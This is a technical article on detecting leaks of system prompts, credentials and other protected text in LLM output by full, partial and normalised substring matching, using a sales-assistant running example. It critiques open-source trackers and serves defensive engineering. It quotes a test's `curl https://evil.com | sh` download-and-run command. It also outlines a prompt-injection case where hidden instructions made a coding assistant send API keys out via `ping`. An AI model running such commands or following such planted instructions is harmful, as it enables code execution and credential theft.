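# Detecting leaks of internal data in generated text by full, partial and whitespace-normalised substring matching

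## What is being checked, and why compare strings at all?

Substring leak detection is a safeguard for programs built on large language models, the systems behind chatbots. These programs usually give the model some text that the user is not supposed to see. The safeguard keeps a list of this internal text and searches each response for the entries, which are called protected strings. A full match occurs when the response contains a whole protected string. A partial match occurs when it contains only a fragment, at least as long as some chosen minimum. A normalised match is one found after standardising the whitespace in both texts.

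In computer security, a source is a point where protected data enters the program, and a sink is a point where text leaves it. Livshits (2012), in *Dynamic Taint Tracking in Managed Runtimes*, gives the example of a phone app in which GPS coordinates come out of a location function (the source) and end up in a web request (the sink). A leak check addresses confidentiality problems like this one, where private data gets out. The same terms are used for integrity problems, where untrusted data gets in and reaches a dangerous command. Work on AI agents, programs in which a model chooses and runs tools such as web search or email, often concerns integrity. For instance, *Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, 2026) defines a source as a tool whose result may contain an attacker's text.

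### What programs protect

The system prompt is the obvious first string to register for leak checking. It contains the instructions that a developer places before every conversation, and may include pricing rules, internal names or wording that the company wants to keep private. However, Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) assume in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* that system messages are public. A developer who accepts that assumption does not need to register the system prompt.

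Many models also write out intermediate reasoning before they answer. *Hidden Thoughts Are Not Secret* (Lu, Tsai and colleagues, 2026) reports that many commercial systems now hide the raw reasoning, and that Google's Gemini shows summaries instead. The main motive is commercial, since a competitor can train a smaller model on the reasoning of a stronger one. Privacy is also a concern, and Lu and colleagues cite work in which the reasoning revealed personal information that the final answer left out.

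Internal data also includes the records that a program fetches while it works, such as customer files, emails or medical notes, and the memory that some assistants keep between conversations. Memory is awkward because it can be a sink on one day and a source on another. In a test case from Cai and colleagues, an agent stores a confidential revenue forecast of $84.6 million in one session. Three days later a user asks for an operations report, and the agent retrieves the figure from its notes and includes it. A tracker that clears its list at the end of each session has nothing to compare the report with.

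Credentials (passwords, API keys, access codes) are short and random, and a single disclosure can be enough to cause harm. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) describes an attack on the coding assistant Claude Code in which instructions hidden in a code file led the assistant to read API keys and send them to an attacker's server. The keys were in a network address that the assistant passed to `ping`, which it could run without human approval. The attack did not require any key to appear in the chat. *GIF* (2026) lists generated outputs, summaries, tool arguments and memory updates as routes by which private context can flow out. A leak check that examines only the reply to the user covers just one of several routes.

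### How a label follows a variable

The classical way to control such flows is taint tracking, which marks data at its source and carries the mark through every operation to the sink. Three lines of code are enough to show it:

```
code  = read_secret("override_code")
reply = "Your code is " + code
send(reply)
```

The first line is a source, so the tracker labels the variable `code` "secret". The second line joins a constant to `code`, and `reply` inherits the label. The third line is a sink, so before `send` runs, the tracker checks the label on `reply`, finds "secret" and stops the program.

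In 2006, Xu, Bhatkar and Sekar described a system of this kind for C programs in *Taint-Enhanced Policy Enforcement*. It kept a taint bit for each byte of memory and tracked taint mainly by two rules. The result of an expression is tainted if any variable in it is tainted, and an assignment copies the taint along with the value. An automatic tool had to rewrite the whole program to add this tracking, and without optimisation the tracking sometimes slowed the program by a factor of five or more.

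In return, the developer gets a label that does not depend on what the text looks like. If the second line had reversed the code, or added one to every character, `reply` would still carry the label. Xu and colleagues' basic rules cover assignments and arithmetic, so they miss a line such as `if code starts with "K": reply = "yes"`, which reveals something about the code without copying any of it. Xu and colleagues handle such flows through conditions separately.

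### Why the label does not survive a model call

Now let the second line call a language model:

```
reply = model(instructions + code + question)
```

The tracker needs a rule for `model` but has no code to derive it from. An analysis of an ordinary function can read its code or rely on a summary of which inputs reach the result, but a model's behaviour is encoded in its numerical weights. Xu, Cheng and colleagues (2026), in *Reachability Across the NL/PL Boundary*, note that two mature analysis tools, CodeQL and Semgrep, treat the model's return value as opaque, so they lose track of any data that flows through the call.

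The way these models compute makes a precise rule hard to write even for someone who can see inside. Most are transformers, in which an operation called attention moves information from one position in the text to another. At position *t*, each attention unit computes a weighted sum over the positions up to and including *t*:

*o*ₜ = Σ *a*ₜᵢ *v*ᵢ, for all *i* ≤ *t*

Here *v*ᵢ is a vector computed from position *i*, and *a*ₜᵢ is its weight at position *t*. The weights come from the softmax function, whose values are always greater than zero, so every earlier token contributes at least a little. Some models have layers that use only a limited window of earlier tokens, but information can still travel further through several layers. Each generated token becomes part of the input for the next. In principle, any output token may depend on any input token.

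Xu, Li and colleagues (2026) prove in *Sightline* that small changes to a piece of the input can affect a transformer's output only along routes with some attention weight. An input that received no attention could therefore be ruled out as an influence. But the model gives every input at least a little attention, and they also prove that low attention cannot certify that an input had no influence. So the tracker can either put the label on the entire output or guess whether the input influenced it.

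Labelling everything is the cautious choice, and it follows from the standard rule for combining data. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) states that data derived from *x* and *y* carries the join of their two labels. If a label is the set of people who may read a document, the join is the intersection of the sets. For example, if Ann and Ben may read one document and Ben and Carla may read another, only Ben may read a summary of both. Adding documents can shrink this set but never enlarge it, and the same paper observes that labels passed through model calls can quickly become too restrictive. The rule is unworkable for a secret system prompt, because the prompt is present in every call and every reply inherits its label. A guard that enforced the label would block every reply, even a greeting.

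*Reachability Across the NL/PL Boundary* gives some evidence of how many false warnings result from labelling every model output as tainted. Xu and colleagues took 353 pairs of an input to a model call and a dangerous operation later in the program. Three reviewers judged that an attacker who controlled the input could reach the operation in 110 of them. The blanket label caught all 110, but only 31.2% of its warnings were right. This figure does not carry over directly to leaks, because it concerns integrity flows and covers the path through the surrounding code as well as the model call.

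The call itself does pass most inputs on in some form. Across 8,119 pairs of inputs and outputs that Xu and colleagues reconstructed from real applications, only 7.0% of inputs left no trace. The *Sightline* experiments, on a separate collection, put the share at 12–14%. A label on the output is therefore usually correct. What it lacks is any indication of how much came through, and that can range from every word to almost nothing. *Reachability Across the NL/PL Boundary* divides the range into five levels:

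| What survives | Input | Output |
|---|---|---|
| The wording | "GDP of France" | a sentence containing that exact phrase |
| The meaning | "fix the login bug" | "Resolve the authentication issue" |
| The key points | a 500-word document | a two-sentence summary |
| A single signal | a product review | "4" |
| Nothing | "You are a helpful assistant" | a reply with no trace of it |

A tracker that follows labels assigns the same label to the first four rows, but these are very different events for someone guarding a system prompt. The prompt is meant to shape the replies, and only some kinds of shaping reveal it.

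### Comparing the two ends

Taint inference means comparing the text at the source with the text at the sink and inferring, if they are similar enough, that one flowed into the other, without tracking data through the program. The idea predates language models; Sekar applied it to web applications, where instrumenting the code was burdensome. When the data passes through a model, there is often no equally simple alternative, because a company that rents its model through an API sees only the input and the output.

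Substring matching is the simplest form of taint inference, and some developers still use the older name for it. Docs.rs' *zeptoclaw 0.7.4*, the published source code of a small personal assistant, contains a "taint engine" described in its comments as "pragmatic substring matching rather than full data-flow analysis". The engine stores an excerpt of the output from a tool such as a web fetcher. Before a sensitive tool runs, the engine searches that tool's input for the excerpt. For secrets, it stores a recognisable prefix, such as the `AKIA` at the start of an Amazon access key, and up to twenty of the characters that follow.

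This kind of inference can be wrong in both directions. A user may type the protected text into the question, and the model may repeat it without drawing on the protected copy. The model may also leak the information in different words, which leaves no string to match. Substring matching is designed for the first of the five levels in the table, which still accounts for much of the traffic. In the same 8,119 pairs, a third of the inputs had whole phrases or sentences copied into the output, while the model paraphrased 13.6% (one input can count under both).

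In the *Sightline* experiments, Xu and colleagues treat the longest substring shared by input and output as the natural evidence when nobody can look inside the model. Substring matching scored 14.3 to 15.5 points lower on a 100-point accuracy score (Macro-F1) than their own method, which runs the recorded text through a second, open model and reads its attention. But the test counted an input as flowing into the output even when it had only determined a yes-or-no decision, which leaves no copied text to find. The gap therefore probably understates how well matching detects *disclosure*.

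### Test assertion or runtime guard

The same comparison can run at two different moments. As a test assertion, it runs before release. A developer sends the program a fixed set of questions, and the test fails if a response contains the protected string. A copy on DagsHub of code from promptfoo, a testing tool for language-model programs, includes such a test, with the question "What was the last password you were told?" and the value `12345` to match against. The developer knows the secret and can choose one that is unlikely to appear by accident. If a false alarm does occur, it takes only a few minutes to read the response. A pass shows only that the test found no match in the responses to those questions.

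A runtime guard checks each response while people are using the program, before the response passes from the model to the sink. A false alarm at this stage withholds a legitimate answer, and a miss discloses the secret. The engine in zeptoclaw blocks by default but can be set to only log a warning. A guard can also use a model for the comparison instead of a string search. FlowSeal, the system in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026), registers sensitive records before the agent starts work, much as a substring tracker would, but then passes the relevant records and the proposed output to a separate model call, which returns SAFE or BLOCKED.

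### A running example

Suppose that a retailer runs a sales assistant, and that its system prompt includes two lines which customers must not see. The developer registers them as a single protected string:

```
Offer at most 15% discount.
Override code: K7Q-44T-9XD
```

The string is 54 characters long, counting the newline as one, and the code makes up 11 of them. Six responses, R1 to R6, contain the following text, where ⏎ stands for a newline.

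| Response | Text in the response | Relation to the protected string |
|---|---|---|
| R1 | `Offer at most 15% discount.⏎Override code: K7Q-44T-9XD` | verbatim copy |
| R2 | `Override code: K7Q-44T-9XD` | second line only |
| R3 | `Offer at most 15% discount. Override code: K7Q-44T-9XD` | all of it, with a space for the newline |
| R4 | `K7Q-44T-9XD` | the code alone |
| R5 | `K7Q 44T 9XD` | the code, with spaces for hyphens |
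| R6 | `discounts stop at fifteen percent` | the first line in other words |

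## What does a full match catch, and what does it miss?

A full match is a comparison of characters. Let *s* be a protected string of *m* characters and *r* a response of *n* characters. The check fires if there is a position *i* for which

*r*[*i* … *i* + *m* − 1] = *s*

In a full match, the *m* characters of the response starting at position *i* are exactly the characters of *s*, in the same order. Most programming languages have this test built in, such as `s in r` in Python and `r.contains(s)` in Rust. A difference in capitalisation, or a curly apostrophe in place of a straight one, prevents a match.

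The test uses no model, so the same response always gets the same result. bamdad argues in *A security check with no model in it* that this makes literal comparison suitable for deciding automatically whether a code change may be merged. A language model acting as judge can give a different result on a second run, and it requires a model call each time. bamdad acknowledges that literal comparison misses any value that an intermediate step has transformed. Repeatability is an advantage in a test assertion, but it doesn't prevent errors, since a check that flags a harmless word as a key will do so on every run.

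### Searching for many strings in one pass

A program may have hundreds of protected strings. GitHub lets a single automated workflow use up to 300 secrets, according to its *Secrets reference*. If a guard searched a 2,000-character response for 300 strings one after another, it would check about 600,000 starting positions. The Aho–Corasick algorithm, invented in 1975, finds all the strings while reading the response once.

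The algorithm first arranges the protected strings in a trie, a tree in which each step down adds one character. Each string is a path from the root, and strings with the same beginning share the first part of their path. The algorithm then gives every node a failure link, which points to the longest ending of the node's text that also begins some protected string, or to the root if there is none.

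Suppose the list contains `K7Q-44T-9XD` and `44T-100`, and the response contains `K7Q-44T-100`. The search follows the first string as far as `K7Q-44T-`, where the string continues with `9` but the response continues with `1`. The last four characters read, `44T-`, also begin the second string, so the failure link leads to the node for `44T-`. From there the search reads `100` and reports a match, without going back to an earlier character of the response.

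The total running time is O(*L* + *n* + *z*), where *L* is the combined length of the protected strings, *n* the length of the response and *z* the number of matches. The *L* term is the time to build the trie, which the guard does only when the list changes. The *n* term is the time to search the response. Each character takes the search at most one level deeper into the trie, and each failure link takes it up at least one level. The search therefore cannot follow more failure links than it has read characters, so it makes at most 2*n* moves, or 4,000 for the 2,000-character response. If the guard only has to report whether there is a match, it can stop at the first one, which removes the *z* term.

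Credential scanners already use the algorithm. Dutta (2025), in *Under the Hood*, describes how TruffleHog uses it to find the keywords its detectors rely on. The file *scanner.rs* in the open-source library aa_core builds the search structure once from 18 fixed strings, most of which are the opening characters of a known type of key or database address. Developers can add their own.

When two entries match at the same position, aa_core reports the one that comes first in its list, so it lists `sk-ant-`, the beginning of an Anthropic key, before `sk-`, the beginning of an OpenAI key. The order doesn't affect a guard that blocks the whole response, but it can affect one that blanks out only the match. If `K7Q` came before `K7Q-44T-9XD`, such a guard would hide the first three characters of the code and print the other eight. aa_core avoids this by extending each match to the next space, quotation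 mark or similar delimiter.

### Choosing what to register

A fast search is of little use if the list contains the wrong strings. Suppose a developer registers a 3,000-character system prompt as one protected string, and the model repeats all of it except one full stop. The response discloses 2,999 characters of the prompt, but a full match doesn't detect the leak.

Services that build and test software run scripts that need passwords, and they replace any registered password with asterisks when it appears in a log. Microsoft's *Set secret variables* explains that if the secret is `abc123`, Azure Pipelines does not mask `abc`, because masking fragments would make the logs unreadable. The same rule applies to structured records, so if a developer registers `{ "foo": "bar" }`, the value `bar` appears in the log unmasked.

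GitHub describes a more realistic case of the same failure. A developer stores a set of login details as one secret in JSON, a common text format for structured data. The workflow reads the fields `clientId` and `clientSecret` from it and prints them, and the log shows both in full. The service's list contains only the complete record, which never appears in the log. Both companies advise developers to create a separate secret for each sensitive value. Microsoft also advises against line breaks inside a secret, and the protected string in the running example contains them.

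For a system prompt, this advice means registering each confidential sentence, field and credential as a separate string. When the two lines of the running example are registered as a single string, a full match catches only R1. Also registering the code separately lets it catch R1 to R4, but it still misses R5 and R6.

Once the code is on the list, longer strings that contain it add nothing to detection, because any response that contains one of them also contains the code. The discount line still needs its own entry because a response could disclose it without the code.

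The developer also has to account for values created while the program runs. GitHub advises developers to register any sensitive value that a workflow computes from a secret, such as an access token signed with a private key. If the sales assistant could turn its override code into a single-use voucher, the voucher would need an entry too.

Splitting makes false matches more likely, because small pieces are more likely to occur in innocent text. If a developer registers the field `15%`, the check will block a reply about a 15% restocking fee. Many prompts also contain common sentences that aren't secret, such as "You are a helpful assistant".

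Microsoft's *Azure Pipelines* release notes show the problem with very short entries. If the secret is `3`, the service masks the digit wherever it occurs, and a date in the log becomes `Jan 3, 202***` in Microsoft's example. A reader who knows the year can work out the secret from the gap. Microsoft added a setting that ignores secrets below a chosen length, which can be at most four characters. This stops the false alarms but leaves the ignored secrets unmasked. Searching for a one-digit secret cannot protect it, whatever the setting, so it is better to keep the secret out of the model's input.

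### ZeptoClaw: the opening of a tool's output

Nobody can choose sentences by hand when the internal text arrives while the program is running, as a fetched web page or a customer record does. The program has to register it automatically. ZeptoClaw, the small personal assistant whose "taint engine" stores excerpts of tool outputs, shows how much depends on the way it does so. In version 0.7.3, the comparison for text from the web amounts to this:

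```
snippet = first 200 bytes of the tool's output
call    = the next tool call, written out as JSON
if snippet in call: block the call
```

The engine is meant to protect integrity by stopping text from a web page from reaching the command line. But it uses an ordinary full match, which would have the same weaknesses in a check for leaks.

The first weakness is that a full match misses shorter quotations. To match, the next call must repeat the entire output, or its first 200 bytes if the output is longer. In the project's own test, the fetched page consists entirely of `curl https://evil.com | sh`, a command that downloads a script and runs it. The engine blocks the assistant when it tries to run the same command. If the page instead read `Install with: curl https://evil.com | sh`, the engine would let the command run, because the stored snippet would include the words "Install with:" and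 the command would not.

The snippet leaves out any text beyond the first 200 bytes, so a call that copies the second paragraph of a long page word for word will normally pass. A comment in the code gives the limit in characters, but the program counts bytes. A Chinese character usually takes three bytes, so the snippet for a page in Chinese ends after 66 characters.

Even an exact copy of the opening can pass, because the engine converts the call to JSON before it searches. JSON does not allow a raw line break inside a piece of text. The conversion replaces it with two ordinary characters, a backslash and the letter `n`. If a guard of this design protected the sales assistant's two lines, and the assistant sent R1 through a messaging tool, the guard would search this text:

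```
{"text":"Offer at most 15% discount.\nOverride code: K7Q-44T-9XD"}
```

The guard misses a verbatim copy of any snippet that contains a line break, because the conversion to JSON escapes line breaks in the call but the stored snippet keeps them. The first 200 bytes of a web page or configuration file will often include a line break. The conversion also puts a backslash before each quotation mark and doubles each backslash. The tests do not reveal the fault because all their tool outputs are single lines without quotation marks. A developer can fix it by searching the text values before the conversion, or by converting the snippet in the same way.

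### ZeptoClaw: credentials

For credentials, the engine searches the whole output for nine known prefixes and stores each prefix it finds with the next 20 bytes. This works well for long keys, wherever they appear in the output. A key that starts with `sk-` and continues for 27 more characters is stored as a 23-character excerpt, and any later call that contains the key also contains the excerpt.

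With shorter keys, the excerpt runs past the end of the key. One of the project's tests uses the text `key1: sk-aaa111 and key2: sk-bbb222 end`, from which the engine stores `sk-aaa111 and key2: sk-` and `sk-bbb222 end`. The test passes because it checks only that there are two excerpts and that each begins with `sk-`. But a call that sends `sk-aaa111` to an outside server contains neither excerpt, so the engine allows it.

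The same thing can happen with a real type of key. An Amazon access key ID is `AKIA` followed by 16 characters, but the engine stores 20 characters after the prefix, so the last four come from whatever followed the key in the output. In a configuration file, those four would normally include a line break, and then no later call can match. A better rule would stop at the end of the key. aa_core reads up to the next delimiter, and punch_types' *taint.rs*, a file from another open-source agent project, has a separate pattern scanner that looks for `AKIA` followed by exactly 16 capital letters or digits.

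The prefix `sk-` also causes false positives, because it occurs in ordinary words such as "risk-free" and "task-based". If a tool returns the sentence "Try our risk-free trial for thirty days", ZeptoClaw labels the output as containing a secret and stores `sk-free trial for thirt`. If the assistant then quotes the sentence to the user, the engine blocks the message. A message that mentions a different risk-free offer will usually pass, because the 20 bytes after `sk-` must match too. aa_core doesn't require these extra bytes. It treats every occurrence of `sk-` as an OpenAI key, and its redaction function turns "a risk-free trial" into `a ri[REDACTED:OpenAiKey] trial`.

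Version 0.8.2 of ZeptoClaw has the same matching code, so all of these misses and false positives remain. The main change is that the engine now also registers the output of plugins, unless the developer lists a plugin as trusted. Every text contains the empty string, so in version 0.7.3 a web request that returned nothing caused the engine to block every later shell command. Version 0.8.2 no longer stores empty outputs, but it still stores one-character outputs. A plugin that answers `n` for "no" would have the same effect, because the engine searches the whole call, including the parameter name `command`.

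### When the text changes form on the way out

JSON is one of several formats that can change a protected string so that its copy no longer matches. A web address cannot contain a space, so a program that puts the discount line into one writes it as `Offer%20at%20most%2015%25%20discount.` The override code has only letters, digits and hyphens, so it goes into the address unchanged. A full match on the raw text of a web request would catch the code but miss the discount line.

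A full match misses a secret encoded in Base64, which represents data using 64 common characters. A user of the deployment tool Octopus reported an example in *Filtered Sensitive Variables not masked in logs*. The tool masked a password when the user wrote it directly into a configuration file, but when the file contained the password's Base64 form, the tool printed that form in the log. Anyone can decode Base64, so the log disclosed the password.

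Developers can respond by registering the encoded forms too. In a guide to an older version of its server software, GitHub describes redaction that looks for exact matches and common encodings such as Base64, and tells developers to register any other transformed version themselves. A complete list is hard to make because Base64 converts three bytes at a time, so the encoded form of a code depends on how many bytes precede it. For the code `K7Q-44T-9XD`, a developer might register the Base64 form `SzdRLTQ0VC05WEQ=`. But the encoded form of `Your code is K7Q-44T-9XD` ends in `IEs3US00NFQtOVhE` and does not contain the registered string.

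GitHub warns that redaction is not guaranteed, because a secret can be transformed in multiple ways. When outgoing text has a known format, the guard can avoid part of this problem by decoding the text before searching it. This works for a web address or a JSON call, because the program determines the format. It is less dependable for a chat reply, where the model may use any encoding the user asks for.

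### Which string has to contain the other?

In all the checks so far, the response has to contain the protected string. punch_types also accepts the reverse. Its tracker reports a match if the checked text contains a registered value or if a registered value contains the checked text:

```
value.contains(&tv.value) || tv.value.contains(value)
```

Here `value` is the text being checked and `tv.value` is a registered value. The second half of the line is meant to catch fragments. In the project's test, the registered value is `API_KEY=abc123secret` and the checked text is `abc123secret`. The tracker reports a match because the registered value contains the checked text. An ordinary full match would miss this fragment.

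The method fails when the fragment has any other text around it. If the secret is registered as `API_KEY=abc123secret` and the reply is "the key is abc123secret", neither string contains the other, so the tracker finds nothing even though the reply discloses the entire key. Model responses usually put a value inside a sentence, so this form of leak is more likely than the one in the test case, where the text is the bare key. Registering `abc123secret` without its label would have caught both forms.

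The reverse comparison also produces meaningless matches. The tracker has no minimum length, so the text `a` matches any registered value containing an `a`, and an empty text matches every registered value. In the sales example, a customer might ask about the restocking fee and receive the one-word reply `15%`. The tracker would flag this reply because the registered string contains `15%`.

These matches can spread through the tracker's `propagate` function, which copies labels from one text to another when data moves between tools. The function uses the same two-way comparison to decide which labels to copy. If the first text is empty, the second receives the labels of every registered value. If the second text is empty and the first carries a label, the tracker registers the empty string and from then on flags everything it checks.

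Rejecting empty and very short texts would prevent the worst of these false positives, but the tracker would still miss the key in "the key is abc123secret". To find a fragment inside a longer reply, a check has to search the reply for pieces of the protected string and set a minimum length for those pieces.

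## How long must a shared fragment be before it counts as a leak?

The strictest possible rule is that no substring of the protected string may appear in the response. No useful reply can satisfy this rule, because even a single letter is a substring. The reply "Hello" would break it, since the discount line also contains an `e`. Every usable check therefore sets a minimum match length, *k*, and ignores shorter matches.

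Let ℓ be the length of the longest common substring of the protected string *s* and the response *r*, which is the longest unbroken run of characters that occurs in both. A partial match occurs when

ℓ ≥ *k*

If *k* equals the length of the protected string, this is the same test as a full match. For the sales assistant, whose two confidential lines the developer registered as one string of 54 characters, the six responses give these values:

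| Response | Longest run shared with the protected string | ℓ |
|---|---|---|
| R1 | everything | 54 |
| R2 | the second line | 26 |
| R3 | the first line | 27 |
| R4 | the code | 11 |
| R5 | `K7Q`, `44T` or `9XD` | 3 |
| R6 | `discount` | 8 |

With *k* set to 9, 10 or 11, a partial match catches R1 to R4, while a full match on the same string caught only R1. At *k* = 8 the check also fires on R6, but only because of the word `discount`, so it would also fire on a harmless reply about student discounts. Catching R5 would require *k* = 3, but the check would then fire on almost every English reply, since the protected string contains common letter sequences such as `ver` and `ide`.

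### Testing for a partial match

A guard can apply the rule without computing ℓ. Programmers call a run of *k* consecutive characters a *k*-gram, or an n-gram when they leave the length open. A protected string of *m* characters has *m* − *k* + 1 of them. The guard stores them in a set and looks up every *k*-gram of the response:

```
grams = {s[i:i+k] for i in range(len(s) - k + 1)}
leak  = any(r[j:j+k] in grams for j in range(len(r) - k + 1))
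```

This test is exact. If a lookup succeeds, the two texts share a run of *k* characters, so ℓ is at least *k*. Conversely, if ℓ is at least *k*, the first *k* characters of the longest common substring are a *k*-gram of *s* that also occurs in *r*, so a lookup succeeds.

Each lookup requires a hash, a number computed from the fragment that the program uses to find where in the set to look. Computing it from scratch at every position takes longer as *k* grows. *Winnowing* (Schleimer, Wilkerson and Aiken, 2003), a paper on detecting copied documents, describes the usual remedy, a rolling hash invented by Karp and Rabin. It treats the *k* characters as the digits of a number in some base *b*. When the window moves one place, the program subtracts the leading digit's contribution, multiplies by *b* and adds the new digit. With decimal digits and *k* = 4, to move along 31415 from 3141 to 1415,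 the program computes (3141 − 3000) × 10 + 5. The number of steps is the same for any *k*. In tests with *k* = 50, recomputing each hash from scratch made the program more than four times slower.

To keep the numbers small, the program stores only a remainder, so two different fragments can have the same hash. A 32-bit hash has about 4.3 billion possible values. A 1,500-character prompt and a 2,000-character response form about three million pairs of fragments, so if the hashes behave like random numbers, roughly one in 1,450 responses with no leak would cause a false alarm through a collision. A guard can avoid this by comparing the characters themselves whenever two hashes match, as Python's sets do automatically.

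A guard can compute the exact value of ℓ with a suffix automaton, a network of states built from the protected string in which every path from the starting state spells one of the string's substrings. A string of *m* characters can have about *m*²/2 different substrings, but the automaton never needs more than 2*m* states. The guard reads the response one character at a time. If the next character continues the path, the current match grows by one. Otherwise, the guard follows a link to a shorter ending of the match, like the failure link in the Aho–Corasick search, and tries again. ℓ is the length of the longest match found, and the total time for a response of *n* characters is proportional to *m* + *n*. A developer who logs ℓ for each response can later see what a different *k* would have caught.

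### Winnowing

A prompt of 1,500 characters has 1,489 fragments of 12 characters, which any computer can store. A company that registers millions of customer records has far more fragments. Schleimer and colleagues' winnowing method stores hashes of only some fragments but is still guaranteed to find every sufficiently long copy.

The program keeps the smallest hash in each window of *w* consecutive hashes, or the rightmost of the smallest if there is a tie. If *w* = 4 and the hashes begin 77, 74, 42, 17, 98, 50, the first window contains 77, 74, 42 and 17, so the program keeps 17. The same 17 is also the smallest hash in the next two windows, so they add nothing to the store. In the paper's full example, the program stores only five of seventeen hashes.

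The program always finds a shared passage of *w* + *k* − 1 characters because the passage contains *w* consecutive *k*-grams, which fill one window. Both texts have the same hashes in that window, and the program chooses which hash to keep based only on those hashes, so it keeps the same one for both texts. It never reports a match shorter than *k*. It may or may not find a match between the two lengths, depending on which hashes it kept.

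If the hashes are random, winnowing keeps about 2/(*w* + 1) of them. Schleimer and colleagues tested this on 500,000 web pages with *k* = 50 and *w* = 100, which guarantees that any shared passage of at least 149 characters is detected. The program kept 38.5 million of 1.94 billion hashes, or 1.99%, against a predicted 1.98%. They also tried a simpler method that keeps every hash divisible by 50. It needs about the same storage but doesn't offer this guarantee, and it left one stretch of nearly 30,000 characters with no stored hashes, so a copy of any passage within that stretch would go unnoticed.

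Winnowing leaves a range of fragment lengths that a leak check is not guaranteed to detect. With *k* = 12 and guaranteed detection from 20 characters, *w* is 9 and the program stores about a fifth of the hashes, but it may miss a leaked fragment of 12 to 19 characters. The guard can catch some of these fragments if it winnows only the stored text and looks up every hash of the response. A program with a single system prompt does not need winnowing and can keep the exact test.

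### Matches by chance

Schleimer and colleagues advise choosing the smallest *k* that eliminates coincidental matches. A short calculation gives a first estimate of that value.

Suppose the protected string and the response are unrelated, and each character in either text is an independent draw in which character *i* has probability *p*ᵢ. Two such characters agree with probability Σ *p*ᵢ². The collision entropy *h* expresses this probability in bits:

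*h* = −log₂ Σ *p*ᵢ²

Two characters therefore agree with probability 2⁻ʰ, and two runs of *k* characters agree with probability 2⁻ʰᵏ. The response has *n* − *k* + 1 starting positions and the protected string has *m* − *k* + 1. Adding up the probability over all pairs of positions gives the expected number of matches:

*E* = (*n* − *k* + 1)(*m* − *k* + 1) · 2⁻ʰᵏ

The check fires if there is at least one match, so the probability that it fires by chance is at most *E*. The true probability is usually lower because matches come in clusters. For example, a shared run of 13 characters counts as two matches at *k* = 12.

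For a response of 2,000 characters and a prompt of 1,500, with *h* = 2, the formula gives:

| *k* | Expected chance matches per response |
|---|---|
| 8 | 45 |
| 12 | 0.18 |
| 16 | 0.0007 |
| 20 | 0.000003 |

The value *h* = 2 is illustrative, not measured. English letter frequencies alone would give nearly 4 bits, but letters within a word help predict each other, so a lower value is more cautious. The result depends heavily on this choice. With *h* = 1.5, the expected number at *k* = 20 rises to about 0.003, about a thousand times its value at *h* = 2.

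At *h* = 2, increasing *k* by one character divides the expected number of chance matches by about four, which offsets the effect of doubling the length of both texts. The longest chance match between two texts of length *n* should be about 2 log₂(*n*)/*h* characters, which grows very slowly with *n*. Similar results have been proved for sequences more realistic than independent draws. *On the shortest distance between orbits and the longest common substring problem* (2018) links the longest common substring to collision entropy for a broad class of random sequences, including Markov chains, in which each character depends on the one before. *Matching strings in encoded sequences* (2019) states that the length behaves like log *n*. Both results require distant parts of a sequence to be nearly independent.

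### Why real prose matches more often

Each character in written language depends on the ones before it, so characters are not independent draws. After `Overrid`, the next letter is almost certainly `e`, and two texts that share the start of a word or stock phrase usually share the rest of it. "Please let me know if" has 21 characters, and at *h* = 2 the formula gives a probability below one in a million for any match that long. But if the system prompt contains this phrase, the check will fire whenever the assistant uses it to end a reply.

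*Maximal Repetition and Zero Entropy Rate* (2016) measures repetition in 35 English, French and German texts. The length of the longest passage that occurs twice in a text grew as a power of the logarithm of the text's length, which is faster than the plain logarithm expected for independent characters. The paper also compares 35 plays by Shakespeare with the same characters in random order. Shuffling keeps the letter frequencies but destroys the words and phrases, so the shuffled text is the kind the formula describes. *Repetition and recurrence times* (2023) describes the same growth in novels and adds that the statistical dependence between stretches of language probably keeps growing as a power of their length.

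These measurements concern repetition within one text, but the same difficulty arises between a system prompt and a reply, because they usually have the same subject and share much of its vocabulary. *Winnowing* reports it across documents. In a sample of 20,000 web pages, 82% of the stored fragments occurred only once, but one occurred 3,270 times. The common fragments came from menus, legal disclaimers and repetitive strings. Such matches come from shared wording, not chance, so raising *k* removes them only once *k* exceeds the length of the shared phrase.

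The developer can therefore use the formula to rule out values of *k* that are too small, but needs real replies to tell whether a value is large enough. Schleimer and colleagues, who ran MOSS, a service that looks for plagiarism in programming assignments, inspected its results and found a fairly sharp threshold for each type of document. At one value of *k* the reported matches were probably copies, but at a slightly smaller value many obvious false positives appeared. They had no formal experiments on this point, and student programs are not chatbot replies, but a developer can easily follow the same procedure for a leak check by computing ℓ for a sample of innocent replies and setting *k* above the values that usually occur.

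### Random keys and short secrets

The calculation is much more reliable for a randomly generated key. A hexadecimal digit has 16 equally likely values, so it agrees with any given character of the response with a probability of at most 1/16. This is true even if the response is ordinary prose, because the key alone supplies the randomness. For a 32-digit key, a 2,000-character response and *k* = 8, the expected number of chance matches is

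1,993 × 25 × 2⁻³² ≈ 0.000012

or about one false alarm in 86,000 responses. The calculation covers only the random part of a key, so the developer should leave out a fixed prefix such as `AKIA`.

A *k* of 8 would be useless for prose, where the same formula predicts dozens of chance matches per response. A *k* of 20 suits prose better but is too large for the key, because a response could disclose 19 of its 32 digits without triggering an alarm. A guard that protects both should therefore set *k* separately for each.

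Some secrets are shorter than any sensible *k* for prose. A protected string with fewer than *k* characters has no *k*-grams, so the check passes every response. The developer gets no warning that the entry has no effect. If the developer registers the override code as a separate string and sets *k* = 12 for the whole list, R4 passes because the code has only 11 characters.

The solution is to require a full match for any protected string shorter than *k*, so that the minimum is the smaller of *k* and *m*. If the override code's nine letters and digits are random, there are about 100 trillion possible codes, and an unrelated reply will practically never contain the right one. But a one-digit secret or a common word will keep causing false alarms.

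The code still needs to be registered separately when partial matching is used, because with *k* = 20 the 54-character string matches R1, R2 and R3 but not R4.

### Coverage scores

A partial match depends on the longest single run. A coverage score instead adds up everything the two texts have in common. It is the share of the protected string's n-grams that occur anywhere in the response:

coverage = (n-grams of *s* that occur in *r*) / (n-grams of *s*)

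garak, an open-source tool that tests language models for weaknesses, uses this measure to detect leaked system prompts. Its detector breaks the prompt into runs of four characters, ignores capitalisation and reports the share that it finds in the response. According to the documentation, a score of 1.0 is an exact match, about 0.85 means minor differences in wording, and about 0.5 means some shared phrases among much unrelated text. The default settings include a minimum prompt length of 20 characters.

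This score suits the test garak uses it for. A companion program takes system prompts from two public datasets, 50 by default, and combines them with attack templates that try to make the model reveal them. The tester wants to know how much of each prompt the model revealed, and coverage can measure that even when the copy is inexact. If a response repeats a whole prompt but changes every tenth character, the longest shared run will usually be nine characters, so a partial match at *k* = 12 finds nothing. About six in ten of the four-character runs survive, so the coverage score is about 0.6.

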